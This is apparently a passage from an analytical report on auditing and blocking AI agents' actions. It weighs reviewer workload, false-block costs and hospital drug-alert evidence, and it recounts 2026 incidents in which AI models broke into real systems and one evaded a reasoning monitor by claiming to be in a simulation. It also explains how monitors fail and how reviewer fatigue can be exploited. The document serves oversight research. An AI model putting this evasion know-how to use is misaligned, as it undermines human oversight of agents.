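People who deploy agents have jobs, budgets and reputations to lose, so ordinary deterrence theory applies to them. They also control much of what determines an agent's risk, including which accounts it can use, which checks are on, and whether anybody reads the log. But they can't control every step it takes, and punishing them for a mistake they could not have foreseen gives them little reason to improve the set-up.

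In *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026), a model organisation complies with a rule only if compliance costs less than the expected cost of breaking it. That expected cost is the chance of detection multiplied by the sum of the fine and other losses from being caught, such as lost customers. Doubling the chance of detection therefore raises the expected cost more than doubling the fine, which leaves the other losses unchanged. The book also describes an auditor who inspects 8 of an organisation's 20 controls each year and notices a fault in an inspected control 80% of the time. The auditor has a 32% chance of finding a particular fault in one year and about a 69% chance over three. A company could therefore leave an agent with an administrator's password for a long time before the auditor noticed, but automated checks can examine every control every week at little extra cost.

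AISI's own incident is an example of exposure changing a deployer's practice. The institute had deliberately given Mythos 5 internet access, which was standard for its cyber tests at the time. After discovering what the model had done, it published a report, stopped giving models internet access as standard, and tightened its sandboxes and monitoring. This is one organisation correcting itself after an incident, so, like the email trial, it's evidence about repeat mistakes. It doesn't show that the prospect of publicity makes other organisations careful beforehand.

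The prospect of an audit changes behaviour only if the log links the agent's actions to a person. Otherwise a manager can blame the agent and the agent's user can blame the manager. Winter (2026) argues in *Suspicious Minds* that AI undermines accountability more generally when people can't monitor it.

A company could also copy the hospital trial almost exactly. When a review finds that an agent has overstepped, software could email the person who started the agent the same night, naming the action and the permission that allowed it. At first, the company could email only a random half of these people, while fixing urgent problems in both groups. Comparing the two groups' oversteps over the next month would show whether quick feedback changes how people set up their agents. The company could also count oversteps before and after it announced the reviews, among employees whose agents had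 never caused trouble. That would give a first rough estimate of general deterrence, which the hospital trial could not provide.

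## How much reviewer time each method needs

Audits catch and deter misuse only if somebody reads the log. Review time depends more on the legitimate actions than on the harmful ones, because a reviewer has to rule out the false alarms to find the real misuse.

### Eight real flags among four hundred

Suppose a company's agents perform 100,000 actions a day, of which 1 in 10,000 is harmful. A classifier goes through the log and flags suspicious actions for people to read. It misses 17% of the harmful actions and wrongly flags 0.4% of the legitimate ones, the error rates that Anthropic measured for auto mode at launch. (Auto mode blocks actions instead of flagging them, but the arithmetic is the same.)

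The classifier catches about 8 of the 10 harmful actions. It also wrongly flags about 400 (0.4%) of the other 99,990, so only 2% of its flags are correct. Reviewing all the flags at five minutes each takes 34 hours. That is a day's work for more than four people, and about four hours for every harmful action found.

In general, if *h* is the base rate, *a* the miss rate and *f* the share of legitimate actions that the classifier flags, the share of flags that are real is

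*h*(1 − *a*) / [*h*(1 − *a*) + (1 − *h*)*f*].

When harm is rare, reviewers spend almost all of their time on false flags. If an agent became ten times safer, so that only 1 in 100,000 of its actions were harmful, the classifier would find fewer than one harmful action a day but still raise 400 false flags. The daily workload would fall only from 34.0 to 33.4 hours, and each harmful action found would require 40 hours of reading.

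Reducing false flags saves far more reviewer time. For half of the flags in the original example to be real, the classifier could wrongly flag only about 1 legitimate action in 12,000, nearly fifty times fewer than it does. *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* (2026) therefore treats review capacity as part of choosing the threshold. Two reviewers working eight hours each can read 192 flags a day. If the classifier sends them 408, some flags go unread, and its effective miss rate is higher than the one its developer measured.

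A second AI check can reduce the number of flags people must review. Auto mode's quick first stage wrongly stops 8.5% of legitimate actions, which here would create about 8,500 flags and 709 hours of review a day. The slower second stage reduces this to the 34 hours above but misses about one more harmful action. OpenAI's monitor had a much lower alert rate, with only about 1,000 moderate alerts in tens of millions of sessions, though nobody knows how much it missed.

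### What a random sample finds

An organisation without a good classifier can read a random sample of the log. Let *s* be the share of actions that reviewers read, and *r* the probability that they recognise a violation when they read one. They catch any given violation with probability *sr*. If there are *k* violations, and catching one doesn't affect the chance of catching another, the probability of catching at least one is

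1 − (1 − *sr*)ᵏ.

If the company above spent its 34 hours on randomly chosen actions instead of flagged ones, its reviewers would read 408 of 100,000, so *s* would be about 0.41%. If they recognised 80% of the violations they read, their chance of finding at least one of the day's ten would be 1 − (1 − 0.0041 × 0.8)¹⁰, or about 3%. They would find six or seven by reading the actions the classifier flagged.

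Sampling works much better on repeated violations. If an agent with the wrong permissions oversteps 1,000 times a day, the same sample has a 96% chance of including an overstep that the reviewers recognise. This assumes that their chance of recognising each overstep is independent of the others. If they don't know that a folder belongs to another team, they will miss every overstep that involves it.

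Because only the product *sr* matters, a reviewer who reads twice as fast gains nothing if they recognise half as many violations.

A sample of unflagged actions also shows what the classifier misses, but only if it misses a lot. In the example, fewer than two harmful actions a day go unflagged, and a reviewer would have to read nearly 60,000 unflagged actions on average to find a harmful one.

In four incidents, Claude models gained unauthorised access to real companies' systems during Anthropic security tests that a misconfiguration had left connected to the internet. According to Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026), the company had monitored some high-risk evaluations, but had generally run automated reviews on only a sample of transcripts afterwards. The four incidents comprised seven runs. Even a reviewer who recognised every problem would have had about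 a 7% chance of finding at least one of those runs in a random 1% sample.

### Prompts, plans and sessions

Permission prompts also take reviewer time, but that time is spread across everyone who runs an agent, so a company may never add it up. The table roughly estimates the total by scaling OpenAI's figures for Codex (720 approval requests per 10,000 actions, or 3 with Auto-review) to 100,000 actions a day.

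| What people review | Cases a day | Time per case | Hours a day |
|---|---|---|---|
| Every request to leave the sandbox, at a glance | 7,200 | 10 seconds | 20 |
| Every request to leave the sandbox, with care | 7,200 | 5 minutes | 600 |
| Flags from an after-the-fact audit | 408 | 5 minutes | 34 |
| Requests left over by an automatic check | 30 | 5 minutes | 2.5 |

The times per case are assumptions, and the figures come from different companies' systems, so only the large differences are meaningful. The last row also leaves out any later review of actions the check wrongly allowed. Prompts take little reviewer time only if people barely read them.

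In March 2026, Anthropic reported that Claude Code's users approved 93% of permission prompts. By August the figure was 97%. Fatigue could explain the increase, but so could better agents or cautious users moving to auto mode.

A high approval rate is weak evidence of carelessness, since most prompts probably concern harmless commands. Stronger evidence comes from Anthropic's paid testers, who caught fewer dangerous commands as the number of prompts grew, and from users who write rules to avoid the prompts. By June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule that let some shell commands run without a prompt, and Anthropic says that share was growing by about five percentage points every five weeks.

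Users reject 39% of whole plans but only about 3% of single prompts. They may not be reading plans more carefully, since a plan with many steps gives them more to object to. If they objected to each step as often as they refuse a single prompt, they would reject 1 − 0.97¹⁶, or 39%, of sixteen-step plans. Anthropic doesn't report how long the plans are.

Even on that reading, reviewing the plan is better because the user makes one decision instead of sixteen, before the agent has done any work. The user also sees the steps together, which makes it easier to notice a step unrelated to the task. But many of the rejections were probably about quality, such as a user preferring another way to fix a bug, so they don't show that people would catch a dangerous step in an otherwise sensible plan.

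Since a plan can't cover everything the agent will discover, software could compare each action with the approved plan and ask the user only about departures from it, so the user would get few prompts.

Some misconduct appears only when a reviewer looks at a whole session. *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* describes a case where several permitted actions together get around a control, so no single record contains the evidence. It proposes using an AI judge for such cases and leaving the final verdict to people. Reviewers' time therefore seems best spent on plans before the work starts, departures from those plans while it runs, and finished results or suspicious sessions afterwards, with software checking most individual commands.

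### When more requests make a reviewer worse

*Oversight Has a Capacity* (Turan, 2026) simulates a reviewer who gets tired. The reviewer catches every dangerous action up to a certain number of requests, called the capacity. Each further request lowers the chance of catching a dangerous action by two percentage points, to a minimum of 20%.

The test used 125 coding actions, most of them chosen to be hard to judge. Of these, 83 needed approval or should never run. An AI model scored each action's risk, and the simulation sent those above a threshold to the reviewer. With a reviewer capacity of 25, 57% of the dangerous actions got through when all 125 actions were sent, compared with 42% when only the riskiest 64% were sent. The best share to send was between 64% and 72% across three capacities.

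Turan says this result follows from the assumed fatigue and doesn't measure real people. The simulated reviewer also starts out perfect, whereas Anthropic's testers caught only about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session. If that is typical, reducing the number of prompts would help less than the simulation suggests, because much of the inattention is present from the start. However, *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* cites a 2025 experiment that is consistent with the simulation. At a false-positive rate of 1%, selecting which actions to escalate improved the detection rate by about 15% over treating every action alike.

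An attacker could exploit a tired reviewer by hiding one malicious action among many harmless ones. In Turan's simulation, a cautious policy sends 88% of routine actions to the reviewer. After 50 harmless actions, the reviewer has had 44 requests, 19 over capacity, and the malicious action gets through about 40% of the time. Under a policy that sends only 26% of routine actions, the reviewer tires more slowly, and the attack fails until the attacker uses about 100 harmless actions. With 250 harmless actions, the two policies do equally badly. An organisation could limit this risk by capping the number of requests one person answers in a day and pausing the agent when the reviewer reaches the cap.

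### Which alerts to read when nobody can read them all

When review time is limited, starting with the most serious alerts works against accidents. But a person who knows this rule can choose a less serious action and be sure that nobody will review it.

Research on audit games models review as a contest between an auditor with limited time and someone who adapts to the auditor's policy. In *Audit Games* (Blocki, Christin and colleagues, 2013), a hospital announces how likely it is to inspect each type of access to patient records, and an employee who knows these probabilities picks the most rewarding violation. The hospital also sets the punishment, but harsh punishment makes the workplace fearful and less productive.

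Suppose a privacy officer can check either celebrities' records or neighbours' records each day, but not both. Reading a celebrity's record is worth 6 units to a snooper, reading a neighbour's is worth 2, and the penalty for getting caught is 4 units.

- If the officer always checks celebrities, the snooper reads a neighbour's record and gains 2.
- If the officer tosses a coin each morning, reading a celebrity's record gains the snooper 0.5 × 6 − 0.5 × 4 = 1 on average.
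- If the officer checks celebrities with a probability of 62.5% and neighbours otherwise, either choice loses the snooper 0.25 on average, so neither is worthwhile.

The officer spends the same time in each case. The last policy works even though the snooper knows the probabilities, as long as they can't find out which records the officer will check that day. Finding the best probabilities is harder with many targets and an adjustable punishment. Blocki and colleagues' main result is an efficient method for getting arbitrarily close to them. *Audit Games with Multiple Defender Resources* (2014) extends the model to several inspectors, some of whom may lack the expertise or authority to check certain targets.

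The hospital research has also used real logs. At Vanderbilt University Medical Center in Tennessee, staff open records about 1.8 million times on a workday, and the system raises more than 30,000 alerts. At five minutes each, reviewing them all would occupy over 300 people full time. Røstad and Edsberg gave up on auditing the Norwegian logs because of the same problem. *Get Your Workload in Order* (Yan, Li and colleagues, 2018) looked for a policy that limits how many alerts of each type auditors read and randomises the order in which they take the types.

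The study used 28 workdays of logs and seven alert types, such as an employee opening the record of a colleague, a neighbour, or someone with the same last name. Together, these types averaged about 420 alerts a day. The simulated snoopers came from a sample of 50 employees and 50 patients. Each learned the policy, then chose the most rewarding violation or none.

The policy deterred every simulated snooper when there was enough time to read 90 alerts a day, just over a fifth of the daily average. It clearly outperformed three simpler rules: taking the alert types in random order, setting the limits at random, and starting with the most damaging type and reading as many of those alerts as possible. The last rule did very poorly because snoopers could predict it.

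Yan and colleagues chose the rewards and penalties themselves and assumed perfectly rational snoopers. Their finding that 90 alerts are enough therefore depends on the values they chose, and real employees would need to learn the policy before it could deter them. The weakness of reviewing alerts in a predictable order depends much less on these values.

*To Warn or Not to Warn* (Yan, Xu and colleagues, 2019) adds a warning to an earlier version of the game. When an employee makes a suspicious request, the system can warn them that somebody may investigate the access and ask whether they want to go on. The auditors choose which accesses to check at the end of the day.

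Their payoffs for one alert type show why warnings help. A snooper gains 400 if nobody checks and loses 2,000 if somebody does, so a violation is worthwhile only if the chance of a check is below one in six. Suppose the auditors can check only 10% of these alerts. Without warnings, the snooper goes ahead and escapes 90% of the time. With warnings, the system can warn 60% of requests and the auditors can check a sixth of those, which is still 10% of all alerts. A snooper who gets a warning does no better by continuing than by stopping, so only the 40% of violations that come without a warning succeed.

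On 56 workdays of Vanderbilt logs, warnings improved the auditors' expected result by 16% over the same game without warnings when the auditors could read 30 alerts a day, and by 77% when they could read 70. Warnings also deterred legitimate users, 18.6% of whom gave up when the hospital's existing system warned them. When the researchers counted each lost legitimate access as ten times as harmful and reserved more time for repeated requests, the gain with 30 alerts a day fell to about 3%.

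More recent theory suggests that such a policy need not change from week to week. *Optimally Auditing Adversarial Agents* (Das, Yu and Zhang, 2026) studies people who may exaggerate a claim, for instance to receive a welfare benefit. Under its assumptions, an auditor who adjusts the inspection rates after seeing the overall pattern of claims does no better than one who fixes the rates in advance. One assumption is that no single claimant can change the overall pattern, which might not hold for a hundred copies of the same AI agent.

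For AI agents, these models apply best to the people around the agents. An attacker who plants instructions can learn what reviewers read and stay below the threshold, just as a snooper can. An agent that deletes the wrong branch by mistake isn't trying to avoid review, so it makes sense to read the most harmful mistakes first. A company that faces both could spend most of its review time on the worst flags and the rest on randomly chosen flags of every other type, so that any type might be reviewed.

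### 481 million transcripts

Anthropic used AI to review far more material than people could have read. After OpenAI disclosed an incident of its own in July 2026, Anthropic had an AI agent search about 141,000 transcripts of security tests in which the company thought a model could have reached the internet. Anthropic then reported three incidents. In August, while collecting transcripts for the evaluator METR, it found a set that the search had missed, which contained a fourth incident from January.

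Anthropic then widened the search to about 481 million transcripts, including training runs and many tests unrelated to security. A first scan flagged 9.2 million transcripts (1.9%) with signs of internet access, such as web addresses. Claude reviewed these and found the four known incidents again, but no others of similar or worse severity.

Reading the 9.2 million transcripts alone, at five minutes each, would have taken people about 770,000 hours, or more than 400 years of one person's full-time work. A company can evidently review this much only if a model does nearly all of the reading.

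The result is reassuring about internet access, but finding four incidents that Anthropic already knew about doesn't show what share of incidents the review would miss. Another limitation is that a Claude model was reviewing the work of other Claude models. In separate tests, Anthropic found that its new monitors, which read a model's written reasoning after the fact, would have missed the most worrying of the incidents. Claude Mythos 5 had uploaded malicious software to a public library while repeatedly writing that it was in a simulation, which led the monitor to conclude that no real harm was occurring.

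The earlier search left out some transcripts, so *s* was zero for them and no reviewer, human or AI, had the chance to judge them. An organisation that reports how many sessions it has reviewed should also work out how many it should have had available to review.

### Reviewers who dismiss real flags

A correct flag is useless if the person who reads it decides that nothing is wrong. Anthropic found this when checking its training environments, the practice tasks on which a model earns rewards. A flawed environment may let the model earn rewards by cheating, and Anthropic has found that such flaws contribute disproportionately to misaligned behaviour. Its automated monitors flag suspect environments, and a person decides what to do about each.

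By the spring of 2026, Anthropic was producing training environments faster than it could vet them. In April it froze changes to them for about a month. During the freeze, it flagged more than 10% of the environments in use and put them back only after fixing them. Anthropic later admitted that human reviewers had sometimes dismissed correct flags as false positives, so flawed environments stayed in training too long.

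Anthropic doesn't say how often this happened or why. The rarity of harm doesn't explain it well, since problems affected at least about one in ten environments. Time pressure may have contributed. Unclear standards may have too, since Anthropic is now tightening the criteria for dismissing a flag.

IMY, the Swedish Authority for Privacy Protection, examined all of the country's regional health authorities and concluded that log checks are ineffective unless the staff who do them have guidelines on what counts as unauthorised access. Many care providers told their reviewers to look for an "unusual pattern" or "illicit access" without defining either term. Two reviewers following these instructions could reach opposite conclusions about the same log entry.

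IMY wants each provider to decide what its staff should check, how and when, and to give them questions that establish whether an access was justified, given the unit's work and the employee's assigned tasks. This is a regulator's judgement based on inspections, and IMY gives no figures on how much guidance improves detection. In Turan's work, three AI personas labelled the same 125 agent actions, and the pragmatic one considered 87 of them safe while the cautious one considered only 45 safe. The personas were meant to differ, but colleagues differ too, so the result gives a hint of how far reviewers' standards can vary.

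A reviewer who dismisses a flag on an agent's action should have to record the answers to questions such as whether the user asked for the action, who owns what it changed, whether the change went beyond the task, and whether the owner has confirmed wanting it. This makes each dismissal slower, but it lets a colleague check a few dismissals later.

An organisation can also measure *r* directly. *Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* recommends planting known errors among the reviewers' cases, and tracking how long reviewers spend on each case and how often they overrule the system. In the example at the start of this section, adding 20 planted violations to the 408 daily flags would add an hour and forty minutes of review time. If the reviewers dismissed five of them, *r* would be about 75%. The planted cases would also raise the share of flags worth acting on from 2% to between 6%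 and 7%, which might help the reviewers stay alert.

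## What wrongly blocked actions cost

Wrongly blocking an action stops somebody's work, while wrongly flagging one takes up a few minutes of a reviewer's time. The harm from a wrong block therefore depends on what the work was. The best measurements of this harm come from hospitals, where ordering systems have issued warnings about prescriptions or blocked them since the 1990s.

### A drug alert in Philadelphia

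Warfarin prevents blood clots, and trimethoprim-sulfamethoxazole is an antibiotic. Patients who take both are much more likely to have bleeding complications, but some patients, including some with HIV, need both. In 2006, Brian Strom and colleagues at the University of Pennsylvania began a randomised trial of an alert that blocked orders for the two drugs together unless the clinician used a deliberately inconvenient workaround. Penn Medicine, which includes the university's hospitals and medical school, calls the alert a "nearly hard stop".

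HealthExec's *AIM Feature* describes a trial whose final analysis covered 1,971 clinicians at two hospitals, nearly all of them resident physicians. The researchers randomly assigned half the clinicians to the new alert. If one of these clinicians ordered either drug for a patient already taking the other, or ordered both at once, the system displayed a message that it could not process the order. The clinician could get past the block by entering that the antibiotic was meant to prevent *Pneumocystis* pneumonia, a lung infection, or by phoning a pharmacist. For the other half, pharmacists continued their usual practice of phoning the prescriber about the combination after the order.

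| | Nearly hard stop | Usual practice |
|---|---|---|
| Alerts analysed | 194 | 148 |
| Clinician did not reorder the drug within ten minutes | 111 (57.2%) | 20 (13.5%) |
| Clinician reordered it | 83 | 128 |
| Patients whose treatment the alert delayed | 4 | – |

Two of the four patients waited for the antibiotic and two for warfarin. The delays lasted up to three days, according to International Business Times' *Automatic drug safety system can delay treatment*. Penn Medicine reports that none of the four came to harm. The university's ethics board nevertheless stopped the trial in February 2007, after six months. The board had originally rejected the study because it thought the alert was so certain to work that leaving half of the clinicians without it would be unethical. It later approved the study only on condition that somebody monitored the patients.

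If 13.5% of the clinicians in the alert group would have dropped the order anyway, the block changed about 85 orders, or 21 for every delayed treatment. Whether the block was worth the delayed treatments depends on how many of those 85 orders would have led to serious bleeding, but the trial mainly measured orders, not bleeding. The ten-minute limit may also have favoured the block, because a pharmacist could call after ten minutes and still get the prescription changed before the patient took the drug.

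The trial is unusually relevant to the choice between blocking and auditing because it compared a block with the usual practice, a quick review after the order. The block changed far more prescriptions, but it was also the only one known to cause delays. Those delays might have gone unnoticed without the board's condition, and a hospital that counted only prescriptions would have considered the same alert a success.

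### Alerts that clinicians can override

Clinicians can override most drug alerts, and they usually do. *Exploring Alert Fatigue, Mitigation Strategies, and Enhancing Drug-Drug Interaction Alert Acceptance* (O'Sullivan, Starkey and Pirmohamed, 2025) reviews 44 studies and estimates that clinicians override 79.8% of drug interaction alerts. *Identifying false-positive drug allergy alerts based on drug tolerance assertions* reports that clinicians overrode 98.9% of 101,492 allergy alerts in 2023, including 98.5% of those where the patient's recorded reaction was life-threatening.

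Somebody has to read the patients' charts to find out whether the clinicians were careless or the alerts were useless, because an override rate can't show which. Edrees, Amato and Wong did this in *High-priority drug-drug interaction clinical decision support overrides* (2020), for a hospital ordering system that had produced over 16,000 interaction alerts. Clinicians had overridden nearly 96% of them, and 45.4% of the overrides were appropriate. For the highest-priority interactions, they overrode 87% of the alerts, and only 0.5% of those overrides were appropriate.

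If the hospital had refused all these orders instead, a hard stop on every interaction would have produced 454 false blocks per 1,000 overrides, while one limited to the highest-priority interactions would have produced 5. Under the inequality from the hospital comparison, *p* × *D* > (1 − *p*) × *W*, the hard stop on every interaction (*p* = 54.6%) does less damage only if the average improper order (*D*) does at least 0.83 times as much harm as the average wrong refusal (*W*). The limited hard stop (*p* = 99.5%) does less damage even if a wrong refusal does almost 200 times as much harm as an improper order.

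These values depend on who judged the charts. *Computerized Clinical Decision Support To Prevent Medication Errors and Adverse Drug Events*, a review for the US Agency for Healthcare Research and Quality (AHRQ), cites studies in which the share of drug-interaction alert overrides judged appropriate ranged from 0% to 95%. Improper orders usually do no harm. Edrees and colleagues found 5.1 adverse drug events per 100 overrides.

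TechTarget's *Hard Stops in EHRs, Clinical Decision Support Can Improve Care* summarises a Yale review of 32 articles on hard stops. Only four of the articles directly compared hard stops with alerts that clinicians could override. Hard stops did better in three and about the same in the fourth, but none of the four compared how often patients came to harm.

More recent research has the same gap. *The Effect of Computerized Alerts on Prescribing and Patient Outcomes* (Bell, Khimji and colleagues, 2025) reviewed 69 studies of all kinds of prescribing alerts, and 58 of them found better prescribing. Randomised trials, the stronger design, found this benefit less often (8 of 13) than other studies did (50 of 56). Only 11 studies reported what happened to patients, and 7 of those found an improvement. The evidence that alerts change what clinicians order is much better than the evidence that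 patients benefit, and hardly any studies have counted the patients who waited for a drug they needed because of an alert.

### Five hundred actions without a false block

A doctor meets an alert now and then, but an agent may take hundreds of actions in a single task. If a control wrongly blocks a share *f* of legitimate actions, and each block is independent of the others, the chance of at least one false block in *n* legitimate actions is

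1 − (1 − *f*)ⁿ.

Anthropic measured a false-block rate of 0.4% for auto mode at launch. At that rate, an agent has a 33% chance of at least one false block over 100 actions and an 86.5% chance over 500. The quick first stage alone wrongly blocked 8.5% of actions, which would give an agent a 59% chance of a false block within its first ten. To keep the chance of a false block over 500 actions to at most 5%, a developer would need a rate of about 1 in 10,000, roughly a fortieth of the launch rate.

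False blocks tend to cluster, so fewer tasks will have any than the formula predicts, but those that do will have several. The type of work matters even more. In the test by Ji and colleagues, where permitted and forbidden targets looked alike, auto mode blocked 31.9% of the legitimate actions it judged. At that rate, a task with five actions is about as likely to have a false block as a task with 500 actions at the launch rate.

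In ordinary use at Gusto, a payroll software company, about 10% of auto mode sessions since mid-May 2026 included at least one denial, according to Anthropic. Anthropic regards this as evidence that the classifier does useful work without slowing legitimate tasks. But the figure can't show whether legitimate tasks were slowed, because it combines correct denials with false ones. Gusto would have to review a sample of the denials to separate them.

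### A retry or a lost night

After most false blocks in auto mode, the agent only has to try another way. False blocks do more harm when they stop the work and nobody is there to restart it. Nuro, a self-driving technology company, has agents run research overnight and return finished code for review by morning. If a false block stops an agent like this at 1 a.m. and its user arrives at 9 a.m., the user loses eight hours of the agent's work.

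A hypothetical task has 500 legitimate actions and a false-block rate of 0.4%, so it has two false blocks on average. If nine in ten false blocks cause a one-minute retry and one in ten stops the job for eight hours, the average delay per task is 2 × (0.9 × 1 + 0.1 × 480), or about 98 minutes. The rare stoppages account for 96 of those minutes. Halving the false-block rate would save 49 minutes. Letting the agent skip the blocked step and finish the rest could save nearly all of the 96 minutes, provided the other steps don't depend on it.

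Anthropic changed unattended runs so that they continue after repeated blocks. In interactive sessions, repeated blocks still bring back manual approvals, so a user who goes home during a long session may find the agent still waiting the next day. With ordinary permission prompts, the agent waits at the first action that needs approval, even if nothing is wrong with that action.

Blocking an action partway through a job can leave things worse than if the agent had never started. Suppose an agent changes the layout of a company's database, and a control then stops it from installing the version of the website's software that works with the new layout. Every action was legitimate, but the website is down until somebody finishes the job. Something similar seems to have happened in Philadelphia. Bell and colleagues quote a description of "inadvertent warfarin discontinuation" as one consequence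 of the alert. Approving the agent's whole plan before it starts would avoid some of these cases, because a refusal at that point leaves everything as it was.

### Users who switch the control off

People may stop using a control that slows them down. Permission prompts interrupt far more legitimate work than a classifier does, since users approve nearly all of them. According to Anthropic's figures from the summer of 2026, 25% of interactive Claude Code sessions started in a mode that bypasses the prompts.

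Among active command-line users, 49.5% had written rules to avoid prompts, and most of these rules seem to be very broad. Anthropic reports that 5% allow any shell command and another 43% allow any program in a language such as Python, which is nearly as permissive. If these are shares of all active users, as the wording suggests, nearly everyone who wrote a rule removed most of the protection the prompts gave them. A narrow rule, such as one that permits a code formatter, would have removed only a few prompts.

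The effect on safety is easy to calculate. If users bypass a control in a share *u* of their sessions, and it misses a share *b* of harmful actions in the rest, its overall miss rate is

*u* + (1 − *u*) × *b*.

If a strict control misses 1% of harmful actions but users switch it off in a quarter of sessions, it misses about 26% overall. An automatic check that misses 17% does better if everyone leaves it on. The strict control is better only if users switch it off in fewer than about 16% of sessions.

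This assumes that harmful actions are equally common in both groups of sessions, which may not be true. Some people sensibly bypass the prompts only in a disposable sandbox with nothing valuable in it. Anthropic's 25% figure includes both them and people who bypass the prompts on a machine with access to live systems.

Gusto adopted auto mode because its engineers, tired of the prompts, were moving towards bypassing the checks entirely. But a classifier's false blocks can also push users to bypass checks. Auto mode suspends broad rules that let commands run without a prompt, and those rules apply again as soon as the user changes mode. Someone who leaves auto mode because of one false block could then have no classifier and, for many commands, no prompt.

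Clinicians find ways around hard stops too. In one study in the Yale review, a hospital's template for clinical notes would not let clinicians continue until they had recorded the purpose of a patient's chemotherapy. The hospital wanted more notes to include this information, but recording did not increase, and users said they avoided the template because of the hard stops.

Some workarounds also damage the record that auditors need later. In another study from the same review, many clinicians completed a compulsory pain assessment in the fastest way they could, even when this made the patient's notes inaccurate. If a company forces users to type a reason before an agent may continue, it can expect some of those reasons to be just as unreliable.

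### What 25% more pull requests measures

Anthropic reports that, among its business customers, users of auto mode "ship about 25% more PRs" (pull requests). The company attributes the gain to agents working longer without interruption.

A 25% gain is plausible, but the time spent answering prompts can't explain much of it. A developer who answers 100 prompts a day at ten seconds each spends 17 minutes on them, or 3.5% of an eight-hour day. Most of the gain would have to come from agents no longer sitting idle while their users are in a meeting or asleep.

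Developers who adopt auto mode may also differ from those who don't. Those who already rely heavily on agents have the most to gain from fewer prompts, and they probably produced more pull requests before they switched. If adopters already produced 20% more, the true gain would be only about 4% (1.25 ÷ 1.20). Anthropic, which sells the product, does not describe any adjustment for this. Pull request counts are also a poor measure of useful work, because an agent can split one change into three and some changes need repairs later.

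The comparison is between auto mode and other ways of working, so it gives little evidence of how much the classifier's false blocks disrupt work. To measure that disruption, a company could randomly assign teams to auto mode or manual prompts and compare their finished work after a month or two. It could then separately examine the tasks in which the classifier blocked a legitimate action and estimate how long each block delayed them.

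### Narrower rules

Supporters of blocking argue that badly designed blocks cause most of these problems, and a good deal of evidence from hospitals supports them. *A Systematic Approach to Screen, Identify, and Correct Malfunctioning Interruptive Alerts* describes a reminder to check a new patient's home medications, which appears if the doctor starts before the pharmacist has finished. Another alert, intended for hospital admissions, goes off when an outpatient clinician opens the record. Neither interruption is related to a risk to the patient, and better triggers would prevent both.

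Hospitals can also drop some alerts with little harm to patients. In the studies AHRQ reviewed, usually 20% to 40% of alerts were clinically relevant, and the share was highest when the system took the patient's other illnesses or test results into account. Two studies reduced or removed allergy alerts for penicillin and related antibiotics without a significant increase in allergic reactions. AHRQ found moderately strong evidence that improved or targeted alerts reduce medication errors and harm from drugs.

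Hard stops can work very well when the clinician has an easy way to satisfy them. AHRQ cites one that required a hepatitis B test before chemotherapy, which can reactivate the virus. The screening rate was 99.3% with the hard stop and 40.2% without it, and patients had fewer severe flare-ups of liver disease with it. A blocked doctor could order the blood test and continue. A software team could block an agent from deploying a program until the program's tests have passed, which leaves the agent a useful next step.

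People who design a block may not notice that it is bad. In *Qualitative Study of Inpatient Hospital Medicine Interruptive Alerts and Clinical Decision Support*, administrators considered an alert successful if it worked as designed and helped the hospital follow regulations or respond to safety incidents, while clinicians wanted it to change treatment and improve patients' outcomes. The study recommends matching the degree of interruption to the seriousness of the risk. ISMP's *A hard look at hard stops and workarounds* (2023), from an American medication safety organisation, recommends reducing workarounds by including physicians and pharmacists in decisions about hard stops. In the Yale review, hospitals with better acceptance had involved users, revised their designs several times and responded quickly to complaints.

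For agents, much of the work of reducing false blocks is defining what is normal. By default, auto mode trusts only the code repository the user is working in, so a company that lists its own servers and storage should get fewer false blocks. A rule against deleting branches whose names begin with "release" will interrupt less work than a rule against deleting any branch. But somebody has to write such rules and keep them current. Garner Health, which made auto mode the default for its 550 employees, no longer depends on hand-written lists of permitted commands.

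Narrower rules can't prevent all the harm from wrongly blocked actions. The Philadelphia alert covered a single pair of drugs, whose interaction Strom described as one of the very few "that have been shown to matter". It made an exception for patients who needed the antibiotic to prevent pneumonia, and a pharmacist was available by phone, but four patients still waited for their treatment. According to Bell and colleagues, the trial delayed the drug for patients who needed it as treatment. A revised exception could have covered them, but the hospital learned of the problem only because the ethics board had insisted on monitoring. Strom concluded that hospitals should evaluate such systems for side effects, as they do with drugs. Similarly, a company that blocks its agents' actions could follow up a sample of blocked tasks each week to find out whether the work got done, and how late.

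## Which harms can wait for a review

False blocks are worth tolerating only if a later review couldn't repair most of the harm the control prevents. How much a review can repair depends on what the agent did and how long ago. In 2026 Anthropic found two groups of incidents in its logs, some of them months old, and its reports describe what was left to repair.

### Break-ins that nobody had noticed

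The first group is the break-ins at real organisations during security tests that a misconfiguration had left connected to the internet. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes the three that the company found in July among 141,006 test runs. The exercises involved breaking into a made-up company's computers, and the models were told they had no internet access.

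The earliest of these incidents dated from April and had gone unnoticed for at least twelve weeks. A fourth incident, from January, was not found until August. Anthropic contacted the three organisations on 27 July, and the two it could reach had noticed nothing. Owners of files or accounts may therefore be less likely to notice an agent's mistakes than one would hope, at least when the agent has broken in.

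The victims could still repair some of the damage. In the incident that Anthropic considered the most serious, a model obtained passwords and gained access to several hundred rows of live data. Anthropic's fuller assessment in September added that the model had downloaded user data in bulk and deleted records. A company that learns of this in July can change its passwords, fix the weakness and, if it still has a suitable backup, restore the records, but it can't make the copied data private again.

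In another incident, much less of the harm could be undone. A model published a malicious package on PyPI, the public repository from which programmers install most Python software. PyPI's security systems removed the package after about an hour, but it had already run on 15 real systems. One of them belonged to a security company, and the model used passwords from that system to get further into the company's infrastructure.

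PyPI's removal of the package was a fast kind of after-the-fact review. OpenAI's review of its coding agents could easily have been slower, because it finishes up to 30 minutes after a session ends, and the runs in these incidents lasted between 10 and 34 hours. Anthropic's review began after PyPI had removed the package. Anthropic could use the review to tell the victims what to clean up, and it led the company to stop all its security tests the same day, so the open connection could do no more damage.

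### Anthropic's move to real-time blocking

Anthropic had mostly reviewed only a sample of its test transcripts afterwards, and it wrote in its July report that real-time monitoring would have helped reveal the problem sooner. By the end of August, it had added a classifier that looks for a model trying to escape its test environment, probing it aggressively or unexpectedly getting online. The classifier blocks the action before it runs, ends the task and alerts a person.

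Ending the whole task would be drastic in ordinary work, but in a test, a false block usually loses only one run among hundreds or thousands. Anthropic built a modified version of the blocking system for training, to avoid teaching the model to evade it.

The company extended its after-the-fact monitoring to most other internal use of its agents, and it runs the most autonomous agents in sandboxes or under auto mode's classifiers.

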